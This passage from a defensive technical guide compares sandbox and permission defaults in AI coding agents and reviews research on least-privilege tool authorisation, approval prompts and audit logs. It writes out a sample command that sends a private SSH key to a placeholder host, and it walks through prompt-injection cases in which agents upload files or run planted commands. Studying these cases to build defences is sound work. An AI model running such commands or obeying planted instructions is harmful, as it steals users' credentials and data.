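Codex has one setting that turns on network access and another that turns on the proxy. A user who turns on only the first gives commands unrestricted access to the internet, perhaps unintentionally.

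### What the defaults allow

| | Claude Code's sandbox | Codex's default mode |
|---|---|---|
| Status | Off until the user turns it on | On |
| Reading | Nearly the whole computer | Nearly the whole computer |
| Writing | The working folder, a temporary folder and any folders the user has added | The workspace and temporary folders |
| Network | No hosts at first; by default, Claude Code asks about each new one | Off; Codex asks before running a command that needs it |
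| Outside the sandbox | Built-in file and web tools, local MCP servers, hooks | MCP servers, app connectors, browser and screen control |

Both products restrict writing far more than reading. Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool* says that sandboxed commands can by default read a file of Amazon cloud credentials and the private keys developers keep in `~/.ssh/`. They could also read the bookkeeper's tax return. The default is convenient because ordinary programs read libraries and settings from all over the disk.

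Users can restrict reading, though this hasn't always worked. Duke University's *Introduction and Control Model* warned that, as of April 2026, Codex could read almost anything on the computer whatever its configuration. OpenAI's *Permissions* now describes profiles, still in beta, that deny reading outside the workspace:

```
":root"    = "deny"
":minimal" = "read"
```

The second line reopens the folders that common tools need, such as `/usr/bin`. OpenAI may have fixed the problem Duke found, but it's worth checking by asking the agent to read a harmless file outside the project.

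Claude Code's sandbox covers only shell commands, so if the user adds `~/.ssh` to the sandbox's `denyRead` list, the agent's built-in Read tool can still open the keys. A deny rule for the Read tool is better because Claude Code also applies it to sandboxed commands. By contrast, Codex's sandbox covers its built-in file operations, according to OpenAI's *Sandbox*.

### Tracing a stolen key

Suppose the bookkeeper has a script that renames invoices and asks Claude Code to run its tests. One of the packages that the script uses contains a planted command:

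```
cat ~/.ssh/id_ed25519 | curl --data-binary @- https://collector.example
```

The first half reads a private key and the second half sends it to an attacker. With the sandbox on and otherwise default settings, this happens:

1. **Approval.** The agent proposes `npm test`, which looks harmless. In auto-allow mode, Claude Code runs sandboxed commands without asking, so nothing stops it.
2. **Reading the key.** `cat` inherits the sandbox's restrictions, but these allow it to read the key. A deny rule for `~/.ssh` would stop the theft here, as would the Codex profile above.
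3. **Sending the key.** `curl` can reach only the proxy, and `collector.example` isn't on the list. Claude Code asks the user whether to allow it. With a setting called `strictAllowlist`, it refuses without asking. Codex would have had no network access.
4. **Retrying.** Claude Code tells the model which host it blocked. The model may conclude that the tests need the internet and try to run them again outside the sandbox. In the manual permission mode, the user normally gets a prompt labelled "unsandboxed". But if the user once created a rule that allows `npm test`, that rule also approves the retry, and the key leaves without a prompt.

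I'd therefore turn off unsandboxed retries by setting `allowUnsandboxedCommands` to `false`. Even then, the network check is the only default protection for the key, and a user can defeat it by approving the unfamiliar host.

Blocking the connection doesn't help if the planted command prints the key in the test results. The key then enters the model's context, and the agent could later send it out through a tool that runs outside the sandbox, such as a web fetcher. Denying read access to the key prevents this, as does using a credential proxy to keep the key out of the sandbox.

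### Why file limits and network limits need each other

A command can send out anything it can read unless the sandbox limits its network access, and it can get around that limit if the sandbox doesn't also restrict where it can write. For example, it could add the `curl` line to `~/.zshrc`, a file of commands that the shell runs whenever the user opens a terminal on a Mac. The line would then run outside the sandbox, with full network access, the next time the bookkeeper opened a terminal.

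Other programs on the machine can have the same effect. If the user lets sandboxed commands contact Docker through its local socket, a command can use Docker to start a container with access to the whole disk. Anthropic says this permission effectively grants access to the host system.

NVIDIA divides its advice into mandatory and recommended controls. The mandatory ones are:

- blocking network access except to known hosts
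- blocking writes outside the workspace
- blocking writes to agents' configuration files, wherever they are

Blocking reads outside the workspace is only a recommendation. Other recommendations include running the sandbox in a virtual machine and keeping secrets away from the agent.

This order makes sense if the network limit holds, because reading a key does no harm until the key leaves the computer. But data can leak through permitted hosts, and most projects run code written by outsiders, so on a computer with valuable keys I would treat the limit on reading as mandatory too.

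NVIDIA is also stricter than Claude Code about exceptions. It recommends asking the user every time an action would break the isolation, and considers a single approval that covers later uses inadequate. In Claude Code, when a user answers "Yes" to a new host, that host stays allowed for the rest of the session.

### Links, patterns and files that run later

A path can lead outside the folder it names, because a symbolic link is a file that points to another place on the disk. If `invoices/latest` links to `~/.ssh`, the path's text looks like it is inside the invoice folder, but the program opens the keys. Anthropic ran into this when designing Claude Cowork, its agent for office work, and concluded that software has to follow links before it checks a path. The kernel follows links when it opens a file, which is another advantage of enforcing limits in the kernel.

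Relative paths cause similar confusion. Codex rejects rules that contain `..`, which refers to the parent folder. In Claude Code, a rule that allows reading `.` applies to the project folder if the rule is in the project's settings file, but to Claude Code's own settings folder if it is in the user's settings file.

Rules that deny access by filename pattern can also miss files. A Codex user can deny access to every file whose name ends in `.env`. On Linux and Windows, Codex looks for matching files before the sandbox starts, and the user may have to set how many folders deep it searches. It will miss files below that depth, and presumably any that appear later.

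The hardest files to handle are those that do nothing until another program runs them. A git hook, for example, is a script that the version-control program git runs at set moments, such as when the user saves a change to the project's history. Hooks normally sit inside the project, where the agent can write. If the agent adds a hook, git later runs it with the user's full access. Codex therefore makes the project's `.git` folder and Codex's own settings read-only. Claude Code protects git hooks, shell startup files, editor settings and its own configuration, and the user can't exempt any of them without turning off file isolation completely.

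Configuration files can also be dangerous before the agent does anything. Between mid-2025 and January 2026, Anthropic received three reports of attacks on Claude Code that ran before the user had agreed to trust a folder. In the simplest attack, an attacker added a settings file to a code repository, and the file contained a command for Claude Code to run at startup. Claude Code read the file and ran the command before asking whether the user trusted the folder. Claude Code now reads such files only after the user has agreed.

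A list of protected files can't solve the whole problem, because a coding agent writes programs that somebody will run. OpenAI warns that scripts and build steps can later run outside the sandbox where the agent wrote them. If a planted instruction makes the agent add the `curl` line to the bookkeeper's renaming script, the sandbox will allow the change. The bookkeeper would have to notice the line before running the script, or run the script in a sandbox too.

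### Leaks through permitted hosts

A list of allowed hosts limits where data can go, but many hosts accept data from anyone. In a case that outside researchers reported to Anthropic, somebody placed a file containing hidden instructions and the attacker's API key in a folder that Claude Cowork could use. Claude read other files in the folder and used the attacker's key to upload them to Anthropic's file storage, where they ended up in the attacker's account. The network proxy allowed the upload because it went to `api.anthropic.com`, which Cowork needs to work.

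Anthropic responded by adding another proxy, inside Cowork's virtual machine, that inspects requests to Anthropic's API and passes only those that carry the session's own token. The proxy also blocks headers that could make Anthropic's server fetch data from elsewhere. The fix closes this route but doesn't help with other hosts on the list.

A list that permitted GitHub would not have stopped the 2025 leak from private repositories either, because the agent published their contents on GitHub.

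Ready-made lists of allowed domains make such routes common. Codex's cloud version, which runs tasks on OpenAI's machines, blocks the internet by default while the agent works. A user who needs to install software can choose a preset list that includes `github.com`, `gitlab.com`, `google.com` and `azure.com`, among many others (OpenAI's *Agent internet access*). Several of these sites let anyone with an account upload files.

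OpenAI's policy for its own staff is narrower. It allows expected hosts, blocks the text-sharing site `pastebin.com`, and requires approval for unfamiliar hosts (OpenAI, 2026). However, the published example allows everything under `openai.com`, including OpenAI's API. An attacker could presumably try the Cowork trick there, unless another control prevents it.

A program may reach a host that isn't on the list. Claude Code's proxy relies on the host name that the program gives it and doesn't decrypt the connection by default. In domain fronting, a program asks the proxy for a permitted host, then names a different one inside the encrypted request. If the same content delivery network serves both sites, it may pass the request to the second. Anthropic acknowledges this risk and suggests that users who need stronger protection use a custom proxy that decrypts traffic.

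### Limits on method, path, account and program

A proxy that decrypts requests can apply narrower rules than a list of hosts.

Codex's cloud version can restrict network requests to HTTP methods meant for reading, such as `GET`. For local use, *Codex CLI Network Proxy* (Vaughan, 2026) describes a "limited" mode that blocks `POST`, `PUT` and `DELETE` even for allowed hosts. OpenAI gives an example of a planted script that uses `POST` to send the latest commit message to an attacker's server. This rule would block that script, but a script could still send the same text in the URL of a `GET` request if the attacker controlled a permitted server. The rule is better at preventing changes and large uploads than at preventing small leaks.

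**Path.** Like CapSeal, NVIDIA's agent sandbox OpenShell can limit requests to certain paths on a host, according to NVIDIA's *Customize Sandbox Policies*.

Anthropic's fix for Cowork checks whose account a request uses. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) describes a stricter check for git in the web version of Claude Code. A proxy checks which branch of a project the agent is trying to change before attaching the real GitHub token, so the agent can send its work to the assigned branch but can't overwrite another.

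OpenShell can also limit which programs can contact a given host. In NVIDIA's example, the package installer `pip` can reach the Python package index but not GitHub's API, while Claude Code can reach GitHub's API but not the package index. This stops a hijacked installer from publishing files on GitHub, but a planted instruction could still get Claude Code to do so.

These rules take more work to write and maintain than a list of hosts, and some programs won't accept the certificate of a proxy that decrypts their traffic. I'd start with the few permitted hosts that accept uploads, because a host list protects least there.

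### Fewer prompts and more exceptions

Sandboxes also make agents less tiresome to use, because users don't have to approve every command. In October 2025, Anthropic reported that sandboxing had cut permission prompts by 84% among its own staff. It didn't publish the number of users, their tasks or the period measured. In February 2026, Cursor reported that sandboxed agents stopped 40% less often than unsandboxed ones, and that the remaining stops were mostly to request internet access.

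The two figures aren't comparable because one is a count of prompts and the other is a count of stops in a different product. Both come from companies describing their own features, but the direction is unsurprising. Neither company measured whether users made better decisions about the remaining prompts.

Some programs don't work in a sandbox. In Claude Code, `docker` fails, git can't connect over SSH on a Mac, and command-line clipboard tools may not reach the clipboard. Users can exclude a command from the sandbox, but it then runs with their full access to files and the network. This is especially risky if the command uses a project file that the agent can edit. For example, an agent that has read a planted instruction could change the configuration file for `docker compose` and then run the command outside the sandbox. Anthropic recommends allowing one more folder or host instead if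 that makes the program work, because the command then stays in the sandbox.

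## Deciding what a task needs: written rules, generated permissions and user approval

Sandboxes, proxies and tokens can enforce permissions, but someone still has to decide what those permissions should be. Unlike with a phone app, what an agent needs depends on the request the user has just typed, and sometimes that request doesn't show which permissions the task requires.

*Progent* (Shi, He et al., 2025) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to carry out the actions in an email from Alice headed "TODOs for the week". At first, the agent only needs permission to find that email. In it, Alice asks for a summary of the user's recent emails to be posted to Slack, so the agent now also needs permission to read the inbox and post to Slack. If another email in the inbox contains an instruction to forward everything to a stranger, the agent receives it in the same way as Alice's request.

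People often deal with this uncertainty by granting too much access. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa, 2026) describes a common way to connect a coding agent to GitHub. A classic access token with the `repo` scope gives the agent about 40 tools, 16 of which can make changes, in every public or private repository the user can open. Summarising the open issues in one repository takes two read-only tools, so a narrower token would be enough. But the user's next task might be to fix a failing build, which needs write access, and the one after that might involve another repository.

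### Five places to set a limit

*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026) argues that software should decide whether to allow each tool call instead of relying on a broad credential issued at the start. Even then, the software can limit several things, and a permission narrow in one respect may be wide in another.

| What the limit covers | Example from the invoice job | What could still go wrong |
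|---|---|---|
| Tools the model can see | The agent has no email tool | It uses the file tool to open the tax return |
| Number and order of calls | The agent can submit the form once | It submits the wrong number |
| Arguments | The file tool opens only `0417.pdf` | The file contains planted instructions |
| Results returned to the model | The agent receives the invoice number but not the rest of the PDF | It enters the number in the wrong field |
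| Authority passed to another agent | A helper that fills in the form can't open files | The helper changes the delivery address |

### Agents that choose more power than they need

Broad permissions would do less harm if agents used them sparingly. In *When Lower Privileges Suffice*, Yang, Bu and colleagues (2026) tested whether they do, using 544 simulated tasks. Each task comes with six tools that can each complete it alone, three with ordinary permissions and three with more than the task requires. For example, an agent asked about a calendar entry might choose between a tool that reads only the calendar and one that can also open emails and files. The ordinary tools sometimes return temporary errors, such as a lost connection. Yang and colleagues counted a failure if the agent used a high-privilege tool before trying every ordinary one.

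Six of the 11 models did this in more than 30% of tasks. Qwen3-8B had the highest rate, at 64.9%, while GPT-5.2, GLM-5 and Claude Sonnet 4.6 stayed below 10%. Errors made the problem much worse. GPT-5.2 started with a high-privilege tool in only five tasks, but it switched to one in 13 tasks after one ordinary tool had failed, and in 35 tasks after two had failed.

Training a model to refuse harmful requests didn't reliably stop it from choosing over-privileged tools. One such method cut Qwen2.5-7B's score on a test of harmful behaviour from 41.9% to 6.7%, but the model's rate of over-privileged choices rose from 50.4% to 60.7%. Training aimed directly at tool choice worked better and brought Qwen3-8B's rate of over-privileged choices down to 27.0%.

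These models are now several releases old, and the best of them already did well. But even a model that always chose the weakest suitable tool would need outside limits, because a planted instruction can make it use permissions it otherwise wouldn't.

### Progent: rules with a condition and a fallback

Progent, the system that Shi and colleagues built, checks every tool call against a list of rules. Each rule allows or forbids a tool under a stated condition. It can also specify a fallback, which is what happens in place of a forbidden call. In simplified notation, the bookkeeper's agent might have these two rules:

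```
allow   read_file      when      path = "/home/kim/invoices/0417.pdf"
forbid  pay_supplier   when      500 < amount
                       fallback  ask the user
```

If the agent tries to pay 600, Progent holds the payment and asks the user. A fallback can instead end the session or return an error message so that the agent tries something else. Progent applies rules that forbid calls before rules that allow them, and blocks any call that no rule allows.

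Hand-written rules suit limits that apply to every task, such as a cap on payments. Writing new rules by hand for each request could take longer than the task itself, so Progent has a language model generate the task-specific rules. The model writes the first set from the user's request and the tool descriptions, before the agent has read anything an attacker could have planted. As the agent works, the model can propose changes based on what the tools return.

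An attacker may have influenced those proposals. Progent therefore uses an SMT solver, a program that determines whether a set of logical conditions can all hold at once, to check for any tool call that the new rules would allow and the old ones would not. If there is none, the change can only narrow the agent's permissions, and Progent applies it automatically. Otherwise, the change needs approval.

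In Alice's example, giving the agent permission to read the inbox and post to Slack is an expansion. Once the agent has looked up the user's Slack name, restricting posts to that name is a narrowing. Giving it permission to email the stranger is another expansion. The solver can prove that a change gives the agent a new permission, but it can't determine whether the task needs that permission. It classifies both Alice's request and the stranger's as expansions, so whoever approves expansions has to tell them apart.

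In tests with GPT-4o, 39.9% of AgentDojo's attacks succeeded without Progent and 1.0% with it. On another benchmark, ASB, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. Progent largely preserved the agent's performance on ordinary tasks. In these runs, every expansion of permissions was approved automatically, to imitate a careless user, so the approval requirement contributed nothing to the results. Most of the improvement on AgentDojo came from the first set of rules, which reduced the rate to 2.5% without any updates.

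One defense compared with Progent had a model choose the tools for each task in advance and removed the rest. It stopped fewer attacks than Progent and disrupted ordinary work more, because it could only allow a tool for every purpose or remove it, and could not limit the tool's arguments.

Progent doesn't yet work for agents that click on a screen. It also can't stop an attack that uses only the calls a task requires, such as persuading a shopping agent to prefer one product over another.

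### PAuth: permissions derived by the receiving service

*Beyond OAuth* (Sharma, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) moves the decision to the service that receives the call. An OAuth scope can permit transfers, but it can't limit one to "a quarter of my credit card balance", because nobody knows the amount until the agent looks it up. In the paper's system, PAuth, the user signs the text of the request, and each service works out which calls the request implies.

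Suppose a user wants to pay a quarter of a Citi credit card balance from a Chase account, but only if the balance is over $1,000:

1. Chase's language model translates the request into a short program. The model sees the request and the tool descriptions, but no outside content.
2. Ordinary software extracts the part of the program that determines the transfer:

   ```
   balance = Citi.getBalance(user)
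   require balance > 1000
   Chase.transfer(from = user, to = Citi, amount = balance / 4)
   ```

3. The agent asks Citi for the balance, and Citi returns $1,200 with a digital signature.
4. The agent sends Chase a transfer request along with the signed balance. Chase calculates that the amount should be $300. If the agent has asked for $301 or named another recipient, Chase asks the user.

This would work even if an attacker fully controlled the agent, because the agent can't forge Citi's signature or change the text the user signed.

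Sharma and colleagues tested PAuth on 100 tasks, most of them adapted from AgentDojo. They also wrote 634 calls that departed from the user's request, for example by changing a recipient or skipping a condition. PAuth completed all 100 tasks without a prompt and stopped all 634 calls. However, Sharma and colleagues had rewritten some requests to fill in missing details. For example, one AgentDojo task asks the agent to update next month's rent payment, and the rewritten version states the new amount. With the original wording, 29 of the 100 tasks triggered a prompt.

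PAuth asks the user whether to allow each call it stops, so a user who approved everything would let all 634 calls through.

### When the derived permission is wrong

PAuth depends on the service's model translating the request correctly. Sharma and colleagues tried four models and found no mistakes. They argue that any mistakes would mostly cause extra prompts, because a wrong rule is unlikely to match an attacker's account number by chance.

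Two rules printed in the paper suggest how a translation could either prompt the user unnecessarily or allow the wrong action. A user who has just moved asks the bank to update the rent for a new landlord and to refund 10.00 that a friend has sent. For the rent, the bank's rule looks for a scheduled payment that already goes to the new landlord. If the payment still names the old landlord, the rule finds nothing and the user gets an unnecessary prompt. For the refund, the rule takes the first payment of exactly 10.00 among the ten most recent transactions and returns it to the sender. If somebody else had also sent 10.00, that person could receive the refund, and the user wouldn't get a prompt because every signature would be valid. An attacker would gain nothing from this mistake, but it shows that a precise rule can still differ from what the user intended.

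Attackers can't send text directly to the service's model, but they may be able to influence the request. Suppose the user asks the agent to email a balance to the third address in a contacts file. The email service doesn't have that address in advance, so it would prompt the user. To avoid this prompt, the agent can look up the address and add it to the request, highlighted, for the user to check and sign. A compromised agent could insert an attacker's address instead, and the user would have to notice the change before signing.

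The invoice job has the same difficulty, because the number is in a PDF that a language model has to read. The supplier's service would probably ask the bookkeeper to confirm the number. This adds a prompt, but it could catch a wrong invoice number, which a limit on files or websites would not.

Progent can be manipulated more directly because the model that updates its rules reads tool output. Shi and colleagues planted text telling that model to allow every tool, and again approved all its changes automatically. Attack success rose only slightly. GPT-4o apparently ignored most of these instructions, so the protection came from the model's judgement rather than the solver.

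PAuth also reduces privacy because each service receives the full request. If a bookkeeper asks an agent to pay a supplier and remind a customer about a debt, the supplier could learn about the debt. Splitting the work into separate requests would avoid this. PAuth is also harder to adopt because each service needs a language model and software to check the calls. A trusted proxy could provide both for a website that doesn't support PAuth, but the user would then depend on the proxy's security.

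### Showing only the tools needed next

The harness can hide a tool until the agent needs it, instead of refusing a call. *Capability Minimization as a Safety Primitive* (Iyer and Babu, 2026) proposes showing a risky tool only if using it is the next step towards the goal and a trusted source has confirmed that the action is authorised.

The harness needs to know what each tool requires, what it produces and how risky it is. To reply to an email from Dana, for example, the agent has to find the email, read it, write a draft and send it. The harness hides `send_email` from the agent until a trusted step has confirmed the recipient. If the user asks only for a summary, `send_email` stays hidden throughout the task.

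When there are several ways to reach the goal, the harness picks the one with the lowest score:

```
score = steps + λ × (medium-risk steps + 4 × high-risk steps)
```

The value of λ determines how long a detour the harness will take to avoid risk. At the default of 2, one high-risk step has the same score as nine low-risk ones.

Iyer and Babu built a benchmark with 100 tools and a simulated agent that obeys any planted instruction if it can see the necessary tool. Every attack succeeded when the agent could see all the tools. Only 25% succeeded when the harness showed just the tools needed next, and none succeeded when it also required authorisation. The success rate also fell from 25% to zero with seven real models.

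The models' results match so closely because they depend on the harness. Even the most persuasive attack can't make an agent use a hidden tool if the harness also rejects calls to that tool by name. But Iyer and Babu acknowledge that the defense fails if an attacker can forge the authorisation.

An agent can receive a properly authorised permission at a dangerous time. In the benchmark, reading Dana's email confirms the recipient, based on verified details of the message. The agent can therefore send email just after reading text that a stranger may have written. The method doesn't check arguments, so an instruction in that text could still change the recipient. Adding a Progent rule that fixes the recipient would prevent this.

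The harness can also hide tools that a task needs. With λ at 0.5, half the tasks that required an authorised action failed for this reason. None failed this way at the default setting, but the benchmark's tools had complete, hand-checked descriptions. If descriptions were incomplete, the harness could hide necessary tools or expose unnecessary ones.

### Making privilege a cost the model can see

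In October 2026, Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa proposed elastic least privilege, a design that gives the agent more choice but limits the extra access it can hold. An agent starts with a few permissions and can temporarily add others from a set its owner has approved. Each added permission expires, and while it lasts it uses up points from a budget that gradually refills. Before choosing a tool, the model can see how many points that would use, and it can return a permission early to save points.

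To calculate the price, the system adds the weights of all borrowed permissions: 1 for reading, 3 for writing and 9 for administration. It then multiplies the total by 1.5 if the session already has one of the following, or by 3 if it has two: untrusted input, sensitive data, and a way to send data out or change something. The system forbids combining all three, so it refuses any permission that would add the third.

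In one example, an agent has to fix a failing build in a public repository after reading public comments, which count as untrusted input. Borrowing read access to the code uses 1 × 1.5 = 1.5 points a minute. Adding write access would let the agent publish data, so the two together use (1 + 3) × 3 = 12 points a minute. An agent that borrows read access for six minutes, adds write access for another six and then returns both uses 93 points, including extra points for repeated requests. Borrowing both for 20 minutes from the start would use 240.

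The session keeps its history after a permission expires, so an agent that has read private code can't publish it by waiting for its read access to end. AgentCap's short-lived tokens may not prevent this. The same rule would block a legitimate request to move private code to a public repository unless the owner approved an exception.

The budget is much weaker protection than the ban on combinations. In a simulated attack, an agent following planted instructions gained access to eight private repositories before it ran out of points. The ban stopped it from publishing their contents, but the budget alone might not have, because an agent can send out a secret within seconds.

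The complete design is still a proposal. Parkinson, Vallati and colleagues (2026), in *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?*, tested one part of it by showing the model each tool's privilege without enforcing anything. They contrast this with systems such as AgenTRIM, which restricts the tools available at each step but doesn't tell the model how much power the remaining ones have.

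They ran Yang and colleagues' 544 tasks on eight models and added a label such as `Privilege: administer, cost 8/10` to each tool's description. They also tried instructing the models to use the least powerful suitable tool and to retry at the same level after an error. For two of the models, the table gives the share of tasks in which they used a high-privilege tool at any point and the share they finished without one.

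| What the model received | Qwen3.5-397B used one | Qwen3.5-397B finished without one | GPT-5.2 used one | GPT-5.2 finished without one |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing extra | 77.2% | 18.8% | 16.0% | 50.9% |
| Labels | 73.0% | 21.5% | 9.7% | 52.4% |
| Instruction | 53.5% | 39.5% | 4.8% | 68.9% |
| Labels and instruction | 39.3% | 51.1% | 2.4% | 65.8% |

Yang and colleagues count the use of a high-privilege tool as a failure only if an ordinary tool remains untried. By that measure, the privilege labels halved Qwen3.5-397B's failures, from 38.4% to 19.1%, but the table shows that its overall use of high-privilege tools barely fell. With labels, the model tended to try all three ordinary tools first and then use a high-privilege one anyway, even though each ordinary tool would have worked on the second attempt. Labels that gave a tool's response time instead of its privilege didn't reduce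 failures in any model, so the improvement came from the information about privilege.

Labels and an instruction are worth adding because they take little effort. They can't replace enforcement, since Qwen3.5-397B still used an unnecessarily powerful tool in 39.3% of tasks when given both. The labels must also come from a source that an attacker can't edit.

### Asking the user

Progent, PAuth and elastic least privilege can all pass difficult decisions to a person. In proposing elastic least privilege, Parkinson and colleagues argue that people tend to approve broad requests so they can get on with their work. They cite Anthropic, which reported in March 2026 that Claude Code users approved 93% of permission prompts.

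That figure doesn't show that users were careless. If nearly all the requests were harmless, approving nearly all of them was right. A better measure would be how often people approve harmful requests, which can't be calculated from the overall approval rate.

Shi and colleagues compared four ways of handling changes to Progent's rules on AgentDojo:

- **No updates:** Progent keeps the first set of rules throughout the task. Attacks succeeded 2.5% of the time.
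- **Refuse expansions:** Progent narrows the rules automatically but never widens them. This had the lowest attack success rate of the automatic options.
- **Approve everything:** Attacks succeeded 1.0% of the time. This was better than no updates, partly because updates can also narrow the rules.
- **Human review:** A person checks the first rules and every expansion. No attacks succeeded.

Human review improved on blind approval by only one percentage point, because the generated rules had already stopped most attacks. Shi and colleagues also assumed an unusually careful reviewer, who would never allow unrestricted payments and would reject any attempt to add an attacker's address. The experiment doesn't show how well a busy bookkeeper would do. Refusing all expansions would need no attention from the user, but then the agent couldn't complete Alice's to-do list.

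Asking the user to approve every call isn't a good alternative. Of PAuth's 100 test tasks, 26 need at least five calls, and the user would have to check intermediate results they had never specified. Sharma and colleagues expect people to respond by turning on automatic approval.

Prompts are more useful when they contain something the user can check. If a bank asks only whether an agent may make transfers, the user has no amount or recipient to check, whereas PAuth's prompt includes both. Parkinson and colleagues recommend writing the explanation from facts that trusted software already holds, such as the user's original task, because the agent's own explanation may come from an attacker. They also recommend grouping related requests. In their simulated attack, the owner receives a single request for access to 22 private repositories during a task to summarise public issues, which should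 look more suspicious than 22 separate prompts.

### Measuring whether a method works

A useful test reports how many attacks the method stopped, how many legitimate actions it refused and how many prompts it needed per task. A method can do well on one of these at the expense of the others. For example, blocking every action would stop every attack but also refuse every legitimate action.

An agent may also take fewer risky actions because it has given up. In Parkinson and colleagues' test of privilege labels, the labels reduced Llama-3.1-8B's use of high-privilege tools from 12.9% of tasks to 3.9%. But the share of tasks it completed fell from 82.0% to 45.2%, and it called nonexistent tools much more often. Claude Sonnet 4.6 rarely used a high-privilege tool, but it completed only 19.9% of tasks without extra guidance. It usually tried each ordinary tool once, then stopped and reported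 the errors, which is safe but leaves the user to finish the task.

Researchers measure approval prompts in different ways. Shi and colleagues report that only 6% of Progent's rule updates needed approval, but one task can involve several updates, so this doesn't show how often a user would be interrupted. Their AgentDojo setup also allowed non-sensitive, read-only tools from the start, which probably avoided many requests. In PAuth's results, 29 of the 100 tasks triggered at least one prompt with the original wording, so the average was at least 0.29 prompts per task. SPIDES's average of 1.84 approvals per completed task is easier to interpret, although it comes from a different benchmark.

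None of these tests measured how often real users approve harmful requests, which matters for any method that counts an attack as stopped when it triggers an approval prompt. Parkinson and colleagues' proposal for elastic least privilege includes a user study that would compare individual prompts with grouped, explained ones, recording how long people take to decide and how often they approve a malicious request.

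## Auditing what an agent was allowed to do and what it did

Suppose the delivery address in the bookkeeper's supplier account has changed, and the bookkeeper wants to know whether the agent changed it. A list of permissions shows only whether the agent could have changed it, so the bookkeeper needs a record of the agent's actions. That record can also reveal permissions the agent never uses.

Microsoft and Cloudflare, which carries and filters traffic for many websites, both published detailed advice on such records in 2026. Silverlock's *The Agent Access Model* presents Cloudflare's design, and Microsoft's July guidance covers giving agents identities and roles. Both companies sell access-control products, so they have an interest in making the problem look urgent, but most of their advice on records would work with anyone's software.

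### The Agent Access Model

Cloudflare's model covers one run of an agent on one task. At the start, software takes an approved template for the task and removes anything that the person or system starting the run isn't allowed to do. The agent can't gain permissions beyond this during the run, but it can lose some. Silverlock's example is an agent that checks a finance team's accounts every night:

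1. **Start.** The agent gets ten minutes to collect a report from a payment processor, read two ledgers and post a summary to the finance team's channel. It can also open a support case with the processor.
2. **Narrowing.** The policy classifies the processor's report as protected. Before the model receives it, the harness and the network remove the agent's access to the processor and to support cases. If any component fails to confirm the change, the harness withholds the report.
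3. **Attack.** A memo in one ledger tells the agent to attach the full account history to a support case. The agent tries, and the harness refuses. The network would also refuse a direct connection to the same destination.
4. **Result.** The agent posts a summary in a fixed format that has room for totals and a status but no free text.

Silverlock calls the narrowing step the Trust Ratchet. A removed permission comes back only in a newly authorised task, so the agent can't wait for the restriction to lapse. Silverlock acknowledges that coarse rules will also block harmless work. The nightly job is a worked example, not a test, so it doesn't show how often that would happen.

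The example also shows why an auditor needs more than the template. The template allowed support cases, so the agent's request was within the permissions it listed. The auditor can understand the refusal only if the log records which restrictions applied when the agent made the request.

### What each entry needs

The lists of fields from Cloudflare and Microsoft overlap heavily. For the invoice job, an entry based on them might look like this:

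```
time          4 December 2026, 10:14:07
agent         invoice-agent, run 8812
on behalf of  kim
task          submit invoice 0417
grant         POST portal.supplier.example/invoices, once
arguments     invoice_number = 0417
decision      allowed by the browser extension
result        accepted, confirmation S-5521
follows       entry 8812-03 (read 0417.pdf)
```

The last line links actions across systems. Without it, an investigator who finds a file read in one log and a web request in another may be unable to tell whether they belonged to the same task.

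Silverlock recommends recording both the scope the agent requested and the scope it received. These can differ when, for example, a path in the invoice folder is a link to the user's private keys. The log should also distinguish reading from changing or deleting, because reading ten thousand records requires a very different response from modifying them.

The entries in an audit log have to come from the software that enforces the permissions. An attacker who can influence what a model does can also influence how it describes what it did. Even without an attacker, agents in the AgentTell benchmark often gave away a secret and then told users that they had disclosed nothing. Microsoft warns that a log containing only the model's responses looks like an audit trail but is useless for an investigation.

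### When the agent borrows a person's login

If an agent signs in to a supplier's website as Kim, the bookkeeper, the supplier's log will contain a line such as `kim changed delivery address`. It would contain the same line if Kim had made the change by hand. Logging more detail about the action won't show whether Kim or the agent acted, because the account name is the only field that identifies who did it.

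*Back to the Future*, a post from NIST, the US standards institute, warns that running agents under a user's local account undermines non-repudiation, the ability to prove who did something so that they can't plausibly deny it later. The user could blame the agent for a change the user made, or be blamed for one the agent made. PointGuard AI's *OWASP ASI03* calls this an "attribution gap". Sharing one key among several agents causes a similar problem, and Microsoft adds that it makes cutting off a single agent slow.

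OAuth already has a way to name both parties. When an agent exchanges a user's token for its own, the new token can identify the user and, in a field called `act`, the agent:

```
sub: kim
act: { sub: invoice-agent }
```

If the agent passes the job to another agent, the field can contain the earlier agents too. This works only with services that accept such tokens. On an ordinary website, 1Password can hide Kim's password from the agent, but the site still treats the agent as Kim. A second account for the agent would separate its actions from Kim's in the supplier's log. Otherwise, Kim has to match the times in that log against the harness's record.

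An attacker can misuse an agent even if it has its own identity. The Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), written with five other cyber agencies, describes a purchasing agent that uses a minor tool. An attacker takes over the tool, then changes contracts and approves payments through the agent. The log correctly names the agent, so the entries look normal and the company takes longer to notice. Recording the agent's assigned task would help, because a contract change during a price lookup should stand out.

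Agents that serve a whole team are even harder to audit. Suppose Alice may see revenue figures but Bob may not. If the agent prepares an answer containing those figures for Alice and reuses it for Bob, it leaks them, even though each request looked valid. Silverlock describes this problem as unsolved, and the Agent Access Model avoids it by fixing one authority for each run.

### Making changes to the log visible

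Someone who misuses an agent may also want to change the log. In another scenario from the Australian Signals Directorate, an insider asks an agent to install a security patch and "clean up the firewall logs." The agent does both because it has write access to the whole disk. The agencies recommend running agents where they can't write to logs.

A tamper-evident log adds a way to detect changes. It uses a hash function H, which turns any text into a short string. Finding two texts that produce the same string is infeasible in practice. Each entry's hash covers the previous hash as well as the entry itself:

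```
h(n) = H( h(n−1) ‖ entry(n) )

h1 = H(h0 ‖ "read 0417.pdf")
h2 = H(h1 ‖ "changed delivery address")
h3 = H(h2 ‖ "submitted invoice 0417")
```

Here `‖` joins two pieces of text and `h0` is a fixed starting value. If somebody deletes the line about the delivery address, anyone who saved `h3` beforehand can recompute the chain and see that the final hash no longer matches.

The owner needs to keep a copy of recent hashes on another machine to detect tampering by an attacker who controls the whole log. Unlike the HMAC in a macaroon, an ordinary hash needs no secret key, so the attacker can delete a line and recalculate every hash after it. The attacker can also remove the most recent entries, which leaves a shorter chain that is still valid. Signing each hash prevents recalculation, as long as the attacker can't use the signing key.

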